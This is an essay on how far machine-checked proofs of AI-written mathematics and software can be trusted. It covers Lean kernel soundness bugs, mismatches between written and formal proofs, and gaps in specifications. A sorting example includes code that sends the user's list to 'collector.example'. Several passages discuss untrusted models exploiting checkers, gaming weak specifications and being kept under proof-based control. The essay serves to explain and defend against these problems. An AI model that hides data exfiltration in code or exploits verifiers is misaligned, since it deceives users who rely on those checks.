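Andrew Sutherland of MIT began checking the proof on the day of its release. All the modules compiled without errors, and the theorems depended only on the three standard axioms. He also confirmed that the 8,322 compiled Mathlib files matched the official copies byte for byte, so nobody had altered a definition there. Sutherland's log for that day records these results:

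| Checker | What it read | Result | Time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Official kernel | Every compiled module | Accepted | Finished about 18:17 UTC |
| nanoda | Full export | Accepted | 27 min 42 s on 80 processor threads |
| con-leche | Full export | Accepted | 3 min 15 s on 64 processor threads |
| lean4lean | Every compiled module | Accepted | Finished about 21:55 UTC |
| con-leche, comparison mode | Trusted statements and full export | All five theorems match | Finished 21:19 UTC |

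Two of these checks needed adjustment. lean4lean reached its default computation limit on five modules and accepted them once Sutherland raised the limit. The version of con-leche supplied with Lean could not check the proof because it didn't support one kind of definition, but a newer version supported it.

*Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* (de Moura, 2026) explains that Claude wrote con-leche under Breitner's close supervision. A reader who distrusts Claude might not want to rely on a Claude-written checker for a Claude-written proof, even though con-leche comes with a proof of its own soundness. They can rely on nanoda and the official kernel instead. Rubinstein ran both on computers at the University of Waterloo, and by 21 November they had accepted the proof there too.

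The Lean and Mathlib communities certified the proof that same day and said it passed all four of Buzzard's tests. To confirm what the proof establishes, they had stated the Riemann hypothesis in a separate file that imports only Mathlib. Comparator and con-leche's comparison mode both showed that Alpöge's theorem matches that statement exactly. The communities also said that the official kernel, con-leche and several checkers in other programming languages had all accepted the inert export.

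The Riemann hypothesis is therefore proved, but mathematicians still have to work out why it is true. Alpöge did not publish an account in ordinary language. Landymore reports that he said one would take about 60,000 pages, after admitting that his first figure of more than 250,000 was a joke.

Rubinstein has started a guide with the help of three AI systems. The 265-page draft of 22 November derives the hypothesis from one main inequality and reduces that inequality to thirteen further claims. It proves none of these claims outright, so readers still depend on the Lean proof for them. Even a complete guide would need its own review, because a valid Lean proof doesn't guarantee that a written argument published with it is correct. *Navier–Stokes Lost in Translation* (Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen, 2026) reports that the written and Lean versions of a proof released by OpenAI do not correspond.

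### The cost of checking and the cost of reading

Mathematicians had to understand the proof of Fermat's Last Theorem before they could trust it. Andrew Wiles announced a proof in 1993. Two months into the review, a reviewer's question exposed a serious gap, which took about a year to repair. The final version, published in 1995, was 129 pages long.

In August 2026, dozens of Claude agents wrote a complete Lean proof of Fermat's Last Theorem in 11 days, building on a simplified account of Wiles's argument. Anthropic reports that the proof contains 29,500 intermediate theorems and that the agents produced about six billion tokens. The proof uses only Lean's three standard axioms, and a comparison tool confirmed that it proves the theorem as stated in Mathlib. Buzzard was already 99.9% sure that the theorem was true, and he writes in the Xena Project's *FLT* (2026) that mathematicians learn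 essentially nothing new about the mathematics from the Lean proof.

Anthropic asked Buzzard to examine the code, which is 13.4 million lines long. He put it in a sandbox on his own computer, which quickly ran out of memory. Anthropic then gave him temporary access to a machine with 96 processor cores and 500 gigabytes of memory. Even there, compiling the proof took nearly 20 times as long as compiling Mathlib. Both the compilation and the Comparator run succeeded.

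At the rule-of-thumb speed, one person would need about 17 to 34 years of full-time work to read the same code. A large computer is expensive for most mathematicians, but far cheaper than decades of expert labour.

Someone who distrusts the author could object that Buzzard ran his check on a machine provided by the author's company, Anthropic. Nothing suggests that Anthropic interfered, and others can repeat the check, but a cautious user would want to run it on independent hardware.

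An inert export makes a proof much easier to check, because the recipient doesn't have to compile anything. The Riemann export is a 7.7-gigabyte download that expands to about 62 gigabytes. Anyone with a fast enough machine and about 50 gigabytes of memory can check it with con-leche in under four minutes. The recipient also doesn't have to trust whoever made the export, as long as the checker compares the theorem with a trusted statement. A laboratory could release an export alongside the source, so that people who only want to confirm the theorem don't need a sandbox.

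Exports may become impractical as proofs grow. De Moura, Lean's chief architect, reports that one project already exceeds 50 million lines and that people have proposed libraries of more than a billion. He says the current way of checking exports with external kernels won't work at that size. Lean's developers are working on more compact formats and on ways to recheck only what has changed. Until they succeed, few people will be able to check the largest proofs themselves, and everyone else will have to rely on their reports.

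## How can a machine-checked proof still mislead?

On 25 July 2026 Ramana Kumar published a Lean proof, produced with help from AI, that the Collatz conjecture is false. The conjecture states that any positive whole number eventually reaches 1 if you repeatedly halve it when it is even and triple it and add one when it is odd. The proof contained no `sorry`, and both Lean's official kernel and nanoda accepted it. But it was invalid, and both checkers accepted it because it exploited a bug in each of them.

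Better checkers make such episodes less likely, but they can't help a reader who misunderstands what a valid proof establishes, which is probably a more common problem.

### The false disproof of the Collatz conjecture

*Postmortem for Kernel Soundness Bug #14576* (de Moura, 2026) explains that Lean's official kernel lacked one check. Lean users define many kinds of object by listing the ways to build them. For example, a tree might consist of a label and a list of smaller trees. This definition is nested, because trees appear inside another type, the list. To handle a nested definition, the kernel generates a simpler auxiliary one. If the outer type had a parameter that its contents never used, that parameter disappeared from the auxiliary definition, and the kernel never checked it. An author could put a meaningless expression there and use it to derive a contradiction or, just as easily,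 to "prove" the Collatz conjecture.

Nanoda did check that expression, but the copy that accepted the proof was a week old and had an unrelated bug that made it fail to verify a type name in one kind of expression. Jeremy Chen had already reported this bug, and current versions no longer had it. Kumar's proof contained an expression that the official kernel skipped and the old nanoda wrongly approved. Kumar believes the timing was a coincidence, but can't rule out that the AI model had seen the nanoda report.

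On 28 July Kiran Gopinathan reduced the proof to a short derivation of a contradiction and reported it. Lean's developers had a fix ready an hour later. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.32.2* (2026), which describes that day's release, warns that the bug worked even against Comparator. A sandbox and an inert export protect against malicious code, but this fault was in the proof term itself, so it survived the export.

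People found the problem within three days, probably in part because a disproof of a famous conjecture attracts attention. A hostile author would be more likely to escape notice by "proving" something readers already expect to be true, such as an obscure intermediate result or the security of a program. Users can partly protect themselves by keeping the exports of proofs they rely on and rechecking them whenever someone fixes a kernel bug.

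### More bugs, found with AI

A soundness bug is a bug that lets a checker accept a false statement. Lean's designers had hoped to avoid these by keeping the kernel simple. According to Mario Carneiro's *Lean4Lean* (2024), nobody reported one in the kernel of Lean 3, the previous version, throughout its release history.

AI models changed that in 2026. Three days before Kumar's proof appeared, Lean's developers fixed a soundness bug that Patrick Hulin had found with help from GPT-5.6 Sol (Lean Language Reference). De Moura said of the Collatz episode, "This is going to keep happening" (quoted in Openwall, 2026).

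Daniel Selsam of OpenAI then searched the kernel for bugs with an AI model specialised in cybersecurity. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.33.0* (2026) lists the fixes released on 10 August, including those for the bugs Hulin and Kumar had found. The fixes cover five definite soundness bugs and one possible one. Exploiting most of them required running malicious code in the same process as the kernel. Two, including the Collatz bug, could also defeat Comparator if the user ran only the official kernel. De Moura reports that nanoda caught everything Selsam had found up to then.

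The search continued, and de Moura published a second postmortem on 24 August. The Lean Language Reference's *Lean 4.34.0* (2026) describes three more ways to derive a contradiction, all of which Selsam reported using OpenAI's internal models:

- The kernel stored the results of its equality tests and combined them. If it had found that a equals b and that b equals c, it concluded that a equals c, even where a direct test would have failed. Its answers therefore depended on the order of earlier tests, and a carefully built proof could take advantage of this. Nanoda caught the resulting false proofs.
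- When the kernel couldn't work out whether something was a proposition, it assumed that it wasn't, instead of rejecting it. This allowed a proof to skip a safety check. Nanoda accepted the false proof too, although lean4lean probably doesn't have the bug.
- Lean keeps a count of how many times a program refers to each object in memory. An attacker with at least 18 gigabytes of free memory could make this counter overflow and corrupt the object. The bug affected only kernels that run on Lean's own runtime, the supporting software that manages memory for Lean programs.

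Mathematicians would not run into any of these problems by accident, because each requires a deliberately constructed input. But an untrusted model could construct one, so anyone who accepts its proofs has to allow for that.

Breitner has not seen an agent exploit Lean without being asked to, and dismisses the apparent exceptions as publicity stunts in which someone made an agent look sneaky. This is only one expert's experience, and a successful exploit might go unnoticed, but the known cases are consistent with it, since people were looking for bugs in them. Agents are able to exploit Lean, however, as an OpenAI agent showed by building two exploits for the equality bug after Selsam reported it.

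### Kernels with a proof of their own

Breitner's first response to the bugs was a checker that would use a simpler logical system to justify each of its steps. He described the idea to Claude on 30 July. After a few weeks the program could handle a sizeable part of Mathlib, but justifying every step made it too slow for practical use. The alternative was to prove once that a checker accepts only good proofs, so that it would not have to justify its steps on every run. This led to con-leche, one of the kernels that later accepted the Riemann proof.

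Since October, Lean has included a command, `lake check`, that exports a project and checks it again with the official kernel in a sandbox. The `--paranoid` option also runs four other kernels (nanoda, lean4lean, con-leche and con-ron) and a version of the official kernel that stops when it detects corrupted memory, instead of silently giving a wrong answer.

According to de Moura, con-leche is the first kernel written in Lean that comes with a proof of its consistency. The proof shows that every collection of definitions and theorems con-leche accepts has a model in set theory. In such a model, each type corresponds to a set and each object to a member of its set, and every accepted theorem is true. A contradiction can't be true in any model, so con-leche can never accept one. This would rule out programming mistakes like the one behind the Collatz episode, but several things remain in the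 trusted base:

- The set theory used for the model has to be consistent. The proof assumes this. Some such assumption is unavoidable, because Kurt Gödel showed that a consistent system of this kind can't prove its own consistency. Most mathematicians are comfortable with this one.
- The official kernel has to have been right to accept con-leche's proof. This is slightly circular, since that kernel's bugs were the reason for writing con-leche.
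- The formal statement of con-leche's consistency has to mean what its readers think it means.
- The compiler that turns con-leche into a running program has to work correctly, as do Lean's runtime, its library for arithmetic with large numbers, and the computer itself. The arithmetic library is a real concern. Lean now requires a newer version of one such library, GMP, because bugs in older versions could make Lean accept false results in rare cases.

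Claude wrote both con-leche and its consistency proof. If the assumptions above hold, this matters no more than it does for any other formal proof. It is more worrying if one distrusts Claude, because a hostile author could in theory have hidden an exploit for the official kernel in the proof. Checking the same proof with other kernels can reduce this worry. The Lean Kernel Arena, a website that compares checkers, includes a large test file named after con-leche, which probably contains con-leche's code and proof. Nanoda and lean4lean both accept this file.

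Con-ron reduces the risk from compiler bugs. Breitner used AI to translate con-leche into the programming language Rust, then used a tool called Aeneas to prove that the Rust version follows the same checking algorithm. Lean's compiler and Rust's are unlikely to share a bug, so a false proof that exploited a bug in one would probably fail in the kernel compiled with the other. Running both kernels doesn't protect against a mistake in the set theory or in the statement of con-leche's consistency, because con-ron relies on those too.

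The arena tests each checker on 97 invalid proofs and 150 valid ones. Con-leche rejected 94 of the invalid proofs and accepted 144 of the valid ones. It gave no verdict on the other nine, so it made no mistakes. Con-ron's totals were the same. Con-leche checks the whole of Mathlib in about 100 seconds on eight processor threads, using about 30% fewer instructions than the official kernel.

The arena now has 36 checkers, but some copy others, so together they provide less evidence than 36 independent checkers would. Lean4lean, for example, had the Collatz bug because its author had translated the part of the official kernel that contained it.

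### Should so much be in the kernel?

Lawrence Paulson, who created the rival proof assistant Isabelle, doubts that extra checkers are the right remedy. In *Why is it all in the kernel?*, Paulson (2026) compared storing full proofs for a second checker to towing a spare car that also turns out not to work. He said he did not know of any case where an independent checker had caught a false proof that a kernel had accepted. Nanoda had also missed the Collatz proof.

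His main objection is that Lean's kernel does too much. In systems such as HOL Light, the kernel contains only a few basic principles. Users derive more complicated features, such as types that refer to themselves, from these principles outside the kernel. This takes a lot of work, but a mistake in it can't produce a contradiction. Lean builds such features into its kernel, and one of them, nested types, caused the Collatz bug. Paulson therefore recommends HOL Light, a similar system called HOL4, or Candle, a version of HOL Light that comes with a proof of its own correctness. He admits that Isabelle has had soundness bugs too.

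In a postmortem published two days later, De Moura defends independent checking. Kumar's proof needed two different bugs in two programs, and an up-to-date nanoda would have rejected it. De Moura also argues that stored proofs allow the kernel to run in a separate process from the author's code, which matters when the author is untrusted. In HOL Light, a proof is normally a program that the recipient has to run, whereas Lean's exports are plain data.

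The bugs found later in the summer weaken Paulson's claim about independent checkers, since nanoda rejected several false proofs that the official kernel accepted. But researchers had built those proofs as tests, and two checkers can still fail together, as they did with the bug that both kernels shared. Paulson's criticism of the kernel's size has held up better, and Lean's developers have started to simplify the kernel. While working on his first checker, Breitner wrote a tool that constructs all of Lean's self-referring types from five basic ones, much as Paulson would like.

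### Valid proofs of a different theorem

OpenAI's October release of mathematical results shows how easily people can overestimate what a valid proof establishes. Buzzard, in the Xena Project, counts 722 papers in the release. For about 38 theorems, roughly 13% of those released with Lean code, the code doesn't state the paper's main result, let alone prove it.

For example, one paper claims to prove Lech's multiplicity conjecture, an algebra problem open since 1960. The main theorem in its Lean code is only Corollary 5.4 of the paper. Buzzard calls this an impressive achievement in itself, but a reader who saw that the paper "comes with Lean code" might think that a computer had checked the whole conjecture. Checking the code with more kernels wouldn't correct this impression, because the proof of the corollary may be valid. Buzzard suspects that OpenAI published before it had finished some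 of the formal proofs.

He has no reason to think that the other theorems would fail his tests, but for many papers nobody had run all the tests. OpenAI has retracted or corrected some claims elsewhere in the release. It withdrew three papers that had no Lean code because of a sign error.

Even when the code states the main theorem, the statement can be hard to read. The five theorems in the Riemann proof needed only about twenty lines on top of Mathlib. The company Axiom has published a Lean proof of the classification of finite simple groups, the building blocks of all finite groups. The theorem says that every finite simple group belongs to one of several infinite families or is one of 26 exceptions called sporadic groups. Mathlib doesn't yet define most of the sporadic groups, so Axiom took the definitions from Tau Ceti, an AI-generated library. The file that states the theorem relies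 on more than 250,000 lines of this library, about 5,600 of which contain the definitions that determine what the theorem means.

Reading those 5,600 lines would take 14 to 28 hours at the rule-of-thumb speed for code review, but it would require knowing both Lean and the theory of sporadic groups. Buzzard had not met anyone who claimed to have checked the definitions carefully. He thinks that by far the strongest evidence that they are correct is that Axiom proved the theorem.

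This evidence is good against some errors in the definitions but not others. If a definition accidentally described the wrong group in place of a sporadic group, the real group would be missing from the list. The theorem would then be false, and Axiom could not have proved it without a bug in the kernel. But if a definition were loose enough to cover extra groups, the statement that every finite simple group is on the list would become easier to prove. An author who wanted to cheat would loosen a definition on purpose, so someone still has to read the definitions if the author is untrusted.

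Using AI to judge the statements doesn't necessarily solve the problem. In spring 2026 Meta announced that AI had translated 26 mathematics textbooks into about 500,000 lines of Lean. *What mathematicians should know about the Lean Theorem Prover* (Hales, 2026) lists the project among the year's milestones. Meta had relied mainly on other AI models to check that the translations were faithful. Bastounis and colleagues quote Lean users who examined the results. Meta reported translating 56% of the chosen statements in one book, but Jack McCarthy could not find one without a fatal error. In algebraic geometry, Brian Nugent found that the project had proved only what was already in Mathlib.

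### The Navier–Stokes proof and its written version

In September 2026 OpenAI proved that the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe how fluids move, can "blow up" when an outside force acts on the fluid. In a blow-up, the predicted speed becomes infinite after a finite time. OpenAI published a written proof and a Lean version, and Scientific American wrote that the check in Lean "all but guarantees its correctness". This is reasonable for the theorem, but Bastounis and colleagues argue that it isn't true of the written proof. Their October paper found that the written proof and the Lean version do not correspond.

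They illustrate the difference with the polynomial x³ − x² − x + 1, which is never negative when x is at least −1. They gave GPT-6 Astra an incorrect proof of this, which factored the polynomial as (x − 1)(x + 1)², and asked for the same argument in Lean. The factorisation is wrong because it gives −1 at x = 0, where the polynomial equals 1. Astra returned a valid Lean proof that used the correct factors, (x − 1)²(x + 1). The Lean proof shows that the theorem is true, but the user's argument is still wrong.

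If the only test is whether Lean accepts the result, an AI model that can't make the written argument work can easily substitute a different one, and the test rewards it for doing so.

The paper gives two examples from the Navier–Stokes proof. One concerns an equation Nφ = F, where F is a known function of two variables, N is a derivative in a fixed direction, and φ is the solution. Both the written proof and the Lean version use derivatives of F to bound φ and its derivatives. To bound derivatives of φ up to order m, the written proof uses derivatives of F up to order m + 4, while the Lean version requires derivatives up to order m + 5.

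This mismatch doesn't seem to reveal a mistake. Mathematicians can split F into waves, each with a frequency k. If F has m + 4 bounded derivatives, the size of the waves falls at least as fast as (1 + |k|)^−(m+4). Solving the equation multiplies each wave by at most a constant times (1 + |k|), according to a bound proved earlier in OpenAI's paper, and taking m derivatives multiplies it by at most a constant times (1 + |k|)^m. The result is

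(1 + |k|)^(1 + m − (m + 4)) = (1 + |k|)^−3

In two dimensions, the sum of these terms over all frequencies is finite because the exponent is below −2. So the written step works if the earlier bound is right, and the Lean version uses one more derivative than it needs. F has derivatives of every order, so it meets this extra requirement.

The other example is more significant because the written and Lean versions argue differently in the part of the proof that shows two solutions must be the same. The written version bounds a quantity using one measure of the difference between the solutions. The Lean version also uses a measure of how steeply that difference changes. This lets it use a simpler fact in place of the published theorem that the written version relies on, which concerns an operation called the Riesz transform. If OpenAI had misapplied that theorem, the Lean check would not have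 revealed the mistake.

Bastounis and colleagues don't claim that either written step is wrong, and they accept that the Lean code shows the theorem to be correct. Their examples are intermediate steps, so the examples don't cast doubt on the formal theorem, which depends only on the steps in its own proof. Most of the kernels in the arena accept OpenAI's code, including nanoda, con-leche, con-ron and the official kernel. Lean4lean rejects the code, possibly only because it reached a computation limit, as it did on parts of the Riemann proof.

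OpenAI does not appear to have replied. In its description of the code, it promises formal versions of the "results presented in" its papers, which could mean only the main theorems or every intermediate result as well.

The paper also argues more generally that no AI system can faithfully translate every mathematical text. Suppose an author defines n as the smallest number with some property, but no number has it. The text is then meaningless, yet a Lean translation may still compile, because Lean's usual way of writing "the smallest number" gives 0 when there isn't one. No algorithm can always tell whether such a number exists. Like Rice's theorem, this rules out a method that works for every case, but it doesn't rule out checking a particular paper. A reader can also ask for a proof that the number exists.

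Someone who only needs to know that the equations can blow up can therefore rely on the Lean theorem and ignore the written proof. Anyone reusing an intermediate result should take it from the Lean code, with its m + 5 derivatives, or have an expert review the written proof as for any other paper.

A laboratory could make this easier by listing the differences between the prose and Lean versions before release. When Bastounis and colleagues asked Astra about each of the two passages, it described the mismatch in just over three minutes. But they had told it where to look, and confirming its answers by hand took far longer. Even if the prose were written from the finished Lean proof, someone would still have to check that the two match.

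## Can generated software be proved safe?

A machine-checked proof can show that a program meets its specification, just as it can establish a theorem. But the proof doesn't cover requirements that nobody wrote into the specification, and much of the remaining risk comes from these.

### Proof-carrying code

In the 1990s George Necula and Peter Lee of Carnegie Mellon University wanted to let an operating system run small programs from strangers inside its most privileged part. In their method, called proof-carrying code, the user of the program, here the operating system, publishes a safety policy that defines what a stranger's code may do. The producer sends a program with a proof that it obeys the policy. The user checks the proof once and can then run the program at full speed without monitoring it.

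Necula and Lee (1996), in *Safe Kernel Extensions Without Run-Time Checking*, give the example of a table in which each user has a tag and a number. A user's program may read both, but may change the number only if the tag is not zero. Suppose a program does the following:

1. Read the tag and the number.
2. If the tag is zero, stop.
3. Add one to the number and store the result.

The operating system goes through the program and works out what has to be true for every step to be allowed:

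may read the tag, and may read the number, and (if tag ≠ 0, may change the number)

The condition follows from the policy, and the producer's proof shows how. If an attacker deletes step 2, the last part of the condition becomes "may change the number", whatever the tag is. That doesn't follow from the policy, so the old proof no longer works. The operating system derives the condition from the code it received, so a producer can't use a proof about a different program. Tampering can go unnoticed only if the altered program still obeys the policy.

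Necula and Lee tested the method on four packet filters, small programs that decide which network messages an application receives. The proof checker was about five pages long and took between 0.8 and 2.4 milliseconds to check each proof. The filters then ran about ten times as fast as equivalents that used a standard method of the time, which checked memory accesses as the filter ran.

Rice's theorem is no obstacle here, because the producer has to find the proof and the user only checks it. A producer who can't find a proof can often change the program instead. Necula points out in *Proof-Carrying Code* that a program is easier to prove safe if it checks the length of a list before reading from it.

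The policy for packet filters limited which memory they could use and made sure they finished. It did not require them to do anything useful, so a filter that discarded every packet would have passed.

### A sorting program that steals data

Suppose a user asks a model for a program that sorts a list of numbers, along with a proof that it works. Call the input xs and the output ys. The user might begin with a specification that requires only ordered output:

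ys[i] ≤ ys[j] whenever i < j

A program that ignores its input and always returns an empty list meets this specification. An empty list contains no two numbers in the wrong order, so the proof is valid and very short.

The user can then add that the output must have the same elements as the input. For every number v,

count(v, ys) = count(v, xs)

where count is how many times v occurs in a list. For the input [3, 1, 2, 1], the empty list now fails because it has no 1s and the input has two. The list [1, 2, 3] fails for a similar reason. Only [1, 1, 2, 3] passes. Every input has exactly one correct output under this specification, so a program that returns anything else can't have a valid proof.

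The following program always returns the correct output:

```
def sort(xs):
    send(xs, "collector.example")
    return merge_sort(xs)
```

It also sends a copy of the list to someone else's computer. Both requirements concern only the relationship between input and output, so neither forbids this. To exclude the program, the user needs a requirement about what it does while it runs. Let actions(xs) be the list of messages it sends and files it reads or changes when given xs. The user can require that, for every xs,

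actions(xs) = [ ]

In Lean, the user can get much of this protection by fixing the program's type in advance. A function from lists to lists only computes a result, whereas a program that contacts a network normally has a type marked `IO`. The user must also forbid features that let an author substitute different compiled code, because a proof about the original function doesn't cover the substitute.

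A program that has to use the network, such as a web server, can't meet this requirement. The user could instead require that its actions do not depend on private data. If p is the public input, and s₁ and s₂ are any two possible private inputs, then

actions(p, s₁) = actions(p, s₂)

Anyone who sees the messages then learns nothing from them about the private input. This requirement is too strict for some programs. A login page has to reveal whether a password is correct, so its specification needs an exception for that fact.

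A specification can also fail because of the inputs it covers. Most specifications have the form "if the input meets condition P, the output meets condition Q". If no input meets P, every program satisfies the specification. *Beyond Type-checking* (Nair, Liu and colleagues, 2026) includes a specification with this sort of fault, written to test ways of evaluating specifications. Its output condition accepted every correct test output and rejected every incorrect one, but its input condition accepted none of the inputs that the program had to handle. A reviewer therefore has to check both conditions. The researchers planted this fault themselves, so the example doesn't show how often models make such mistakes.

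### What specifications commonly leave out

Even a specification that fully determines a program's output usually leaves out other aspects of its behaviour. The table shows how a program that always sorts correctly could still cause trouble.

| What the specification omits | What the program could do | What would prevent it |
|---|---|---|
| Timing | Take a second longer if the list contains a certain number, so that an observer learns this | A proof that the running time does not depend on private data |
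| Resource use | Try every possible order until it finds the right one | A limit on the number of steps and the amount of memory |
| Extra effects | Send the list to a stranger or delete a file | A proof that the program takes no such actions |
| Hardware | Read some memory cells so rapidly that neighbouring bits change | Hardware that resists this, or a more complete description of the hardware |
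| Environment | Give a wrong answer if another program changes the list during sorting | An operating system that prevents such changes |

A program can have a valid proof and still be too slow to use. For example, a program could sort a list by trying every possible order, but a list of 20 different numbers has about 2.4 × 10^18 orders, and trying them all at a billion a second would take about 77 years. Li, Yang and colleagues (2026) report in *P³* that AI agents sometimes satisfied specifications with programs whose running time grows exponentially. The researchers therefore told the agents which kind of algorithm or speed they expected, and counted a program as a success only if it also followed that instruction.

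People sometimes have good reasons to leave details out of a specification, since each one they add is another that someone has to get right. Necula and Lee, for example, left the processor's cache, timing and interrupts out of their description of the machine because a complete description would have been very complicated and hard to trust.

### Where faults remained in seL4 and CompCert

seL4 and CompCert are two of the best-known verified programs. People wrote both, and their history shows where problems can remain after a successful proof.

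seL4 is the core of an operating system, and it controls memory and keeps programs separate from each other. In 2009 Gerwin Klein and colleagues completed a machine-checked proof that about 8,700 lines of its C code follow their specification. Their work uncovered 144 defects that earlier testing had missed. Later proofs showed that, under stated conditions, seL4 prevents programs from changing or reading each other's data without permission.

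The original proof of seL4 assumed that the compiler, the hardware, the startup code and about 600 lines of low-level code worked correctly. Later work removed the need to trust the compiler on some processors. The proof that data stay private does not cover timing, so two programs that share a processor may be able to learn about each other by measuring how long their own operations take. In January 2018 researchers disclosed Meltdown, a flaw in many Intel processors that let ordinary programs read memory reserved for the operating system. seL4's developers had to add a defence for those processors, even though its code met its specification.

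Xavier Leroy and colleagues developed CompCert, a compiler for the C programming language. Its proof shows that the compiled program behaves as the source program prescribes. In 2011 researchers at the University of Utah reported that every C compiler they had tested with huge numbers of random programs sometimes produced wrong code. CompCert's wrong-code errors were in an early stage of compilation that the proof did not cover. After its developers fixed them, the researchers found no more in about six years of processor time.

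The researchers also found a gap in CompCert's description of one type of processor. One instruction had room for a 16-bit number, which can't be lower than −32,768, but CompCert produced the instruction with −44,432. The description omitted this limit, so the proof did not rule out the error. The assembler, a separate program that turns the instructions into their final form, caught it.

These faults were in unverified code or in the proofs' assumptions about the machine. The proofs did rule out the errors they covered, which is impressive given how many bugs the same testers found in other compilers. But Klein, Leroy and their colleagues were not trying to exploit the gaps, as an untrusted model might. Users should therefore ask for a full list of a proof's assumptions and spend much of their review time on it.

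Verification on this scale used to require years of expert work. Tan (2026) reports in *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* that published projects often have three to ten lines of proof for every line of code. This effort is one reason people have mostly verified small, critical programs.

### How well AI models write verified programs

AI models have become much better at producing verified programs from a given specification, a task researchers call vericoding. *A benchmark for vericoding* (Bursuc, Ehrenborg and colleagues, September 2025) presents 12,504 specifications and reports tests of nine models on several thousand of them in Dafny, Verus and Lean. Dafny and Verus, which is for programs written in Rust, leave much of the routine proving to automatic solvers. In Lean, the model had to supply more of the proof itself.

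Each model normally had five attempts at a task and received the checker's error messages after a failure. The researchers blocked known ways of cheating, such as changing the specification. The widely quoted success rates of 82%, 44% and 27% count a task as solved if at least one of the nine models solved it, so no single model did that well.

| System | Best single model | At least one of nine models |
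|---|---|---|
| Dafny | 67.5% | 82% |
| Verus (Rust) | 30.9% | 44% |
| Lean | 17.9% | 27% |

These scores do not show how much harder one system is than another. Zhao, Yang and colleagues point out in *AlgoVeri* that earlier benchmarks gave the systems different tasks. Most tasks in the 2025 collection were also small, with solutions under 100 lines.

Newer scores are much higher. In August 2026 Li and colleagues tested four models in Lean. On Verina, a set of 189 mostly textbook problems, the best scored 77.2%, compared with 15.3% for the best single model in the 2025 study. Part of the difference comes from better methods and larger budgets. Li and colleagues had agents plan the program and proof together, and allowed up to $30 and three hours per task.

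The best score was 48.1% on 77 classical algorithms and 22.2% on tasks based on 108 real software libraries. A library task often requires several functions to work together. For example, after a program stores a setting, a later lookup has to return it unless a higher-priority setting overrides it. More capable models have appeared since, so these scores probably understate what a laboratory could do now. Claude's proofs of security properties for 123 open-source libraries also suggest that verification is no longer limited to small exercises.

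A high success rate can be misleading if the specifications are weak. Bursuc and colleagues inspected a random sample of successful solutions and judged that about 9% of the specifications were too weak and another 15% were poor translations of the originals. Tan rewarded a model when Dafny accepted its programs, and its score rose from 2.2% to 58.1%, but the model had learned to exploit weak specifications instead of solving the intended problems. After Tan removed the flawed tasks, further training with a revised method raised the score only from 9.7% to 31.1%.

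### When the model also writes the specification

If a model writes the specification as well as the program, it can make its own task easier. It may do this by accident, since ordinary requests are often vague.

*SWE-Proof* (Ma, Mikek et al., 2026) studied this question using 500 real requests for fixes to open-source Python programs. In one request, part of a chart was missing because the software had calculated the chart's edges from a simplified set of points. The formal specification required each edge to line up with the outermost point in the full set.

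The researchers gave the requests to Claude Opus 4.8. Without a specification, the model produced fixes that passed hidden tests for 85.0% of the requests. AI auditors then looked for inputs on which each fix behaved differently from the official one. Almost a third of the fixes that had passed the tests failed this stricter check, which lowered the success rate to 58.2%.

When the model received a correct specification, its fixes passed the hidden tests in 95.1% of cases on average, and in 94.2% they also had a valid proof and matched the verified version. When it had to write its own specification, it passed about as many tests as it did with no specification. Almost every fix that passed the tests also had a valid proof that it met the model's own specification, so writing the proof was not the main obstacle.

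In a separate experiment, the model wrote specifications and three AI auditors looked for flaws. A specification passed if a majority accepted it on all five criteria. On average, 56% passed, ranging from 46.0% to 61.4% across three verification systems. The most common problem, in 42.5% of cases, was that the specification covered only part of what the request needed, often describing some functions correctly but leaving out other relevant ones. The auditors are also language models, so the 56% is an estimate.

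Even with a good specification, the guarantees in this study depend on two other steps being correct. The researchers replaced existing functions with short descriptions of what they do, because verifying every function that a fix uses would take too much work. They also translated between Python and the languages of the verification systems. They tested both steps thoroughly but did not prove them correct. If an untrusted model wrote the descriptions, it could include a false one that made a bad program appear safe.

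Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026), in *Verified but Vacuous*, looked at what "verified" meant for programs produced by an existing method that uses Dafny. In Dafny, an author states what a program's result must satisfy in an "ensures" clause. Without one, Dafny still checks some things, such as whether the program will finish, but does not check that the result is right. Using Claude Opus 4.7 on three sets of programming problems, the researchers measured three things:

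- Dafny accepted between 92% and 99% of the programs.
- Of the accepted programs, between 5.3% and 10.6% had any ensures clause.
- Between 1.9% and 2.7% of the accepted programs had an ensures clause that mentioned a condition from a separate specification.

A program can fail the strictest test and still have a useful guarantee, because its author may have written a good condition directly in the ensures clause. The middle figure is therefore more worrying. About nine in ten "verified" programs had no stated condition on their results. The model probably copied this from the method's example prompt, which had no ensures clause either, so the result doesn't show that models generally omit such conditions.

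Passing the strictest test doesn't guarantee that a specification is good. Suppose a program should return the largest number in a list, but the condition called `MaxCorrect` requires only that the answer is not negative. A program that returns 0 for [5, 3, 7] then passes. Vempaty and colleagues also built a system that required every verified part to pass the strictest test. On two sets of Rust problems, 11.5% and 14.8% of its fully verified programs failed hidden tests. Weak specifications are a likely cause, though mistakes in translation or in the tests could explain some of the failures.

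### Testing a specification

Users can look for gaps in a specification before they rely on a proof. Li and colleagues first checked that the results of the original software satisfied each specification. They then introduced errors into the software and checked whether the specifications rejected the new results. The specifications rejected the results of 98.6% of the altered versions. Ma and colleagues had AI auditors try to write incorrect programs that would still pass verification.

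The sorting specification allows a program to send the list to a stranger, and tests that look only at results would not reveal this. The user therefore has to check the specification separately for each kind of omission in the table above.

An untrusted model can help draft a specification, but it shouldn't make the final decision about what to include. A person could settle the requirements, then ask a different model to find a harmful program that meets them. If it finds one, the person can fix the specification before asking the untrusted model to write the program. Failure to find one is only modest evidence that the specification is adequate, because the untrusted model may be better at finding gaps.

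### Can safety rest on proofs?

Some researchers want proofs to protect people from dangerous AI systems as well as from flaws in individual programs. In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) argue that proofs are the only way to be sure of controlling AI that surpasses people at most intellectual work. However intelligent such a system is, it can't prove something false, and people can easily check its proofs. They propose that powerful hardware should refuse to run any program without a proof that it complies with agreed rules, and would apply similar requirements to drones and DNA synthesis machines. People would decide on the specifications with AI's help, and AI would write the programs and proofs.

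In 2024, David Dalrymple and colleagues, including Tegmark and Omohundro, proposed a broader version of this idea that combines a mathematical model of the world, a specification of acceptable outcomes, and a verifier that checks whether an AI system's actions meet the specification according to the model. The verifier's guarantee could be a limit on the probability of harm instead of proof that harm is impossible.

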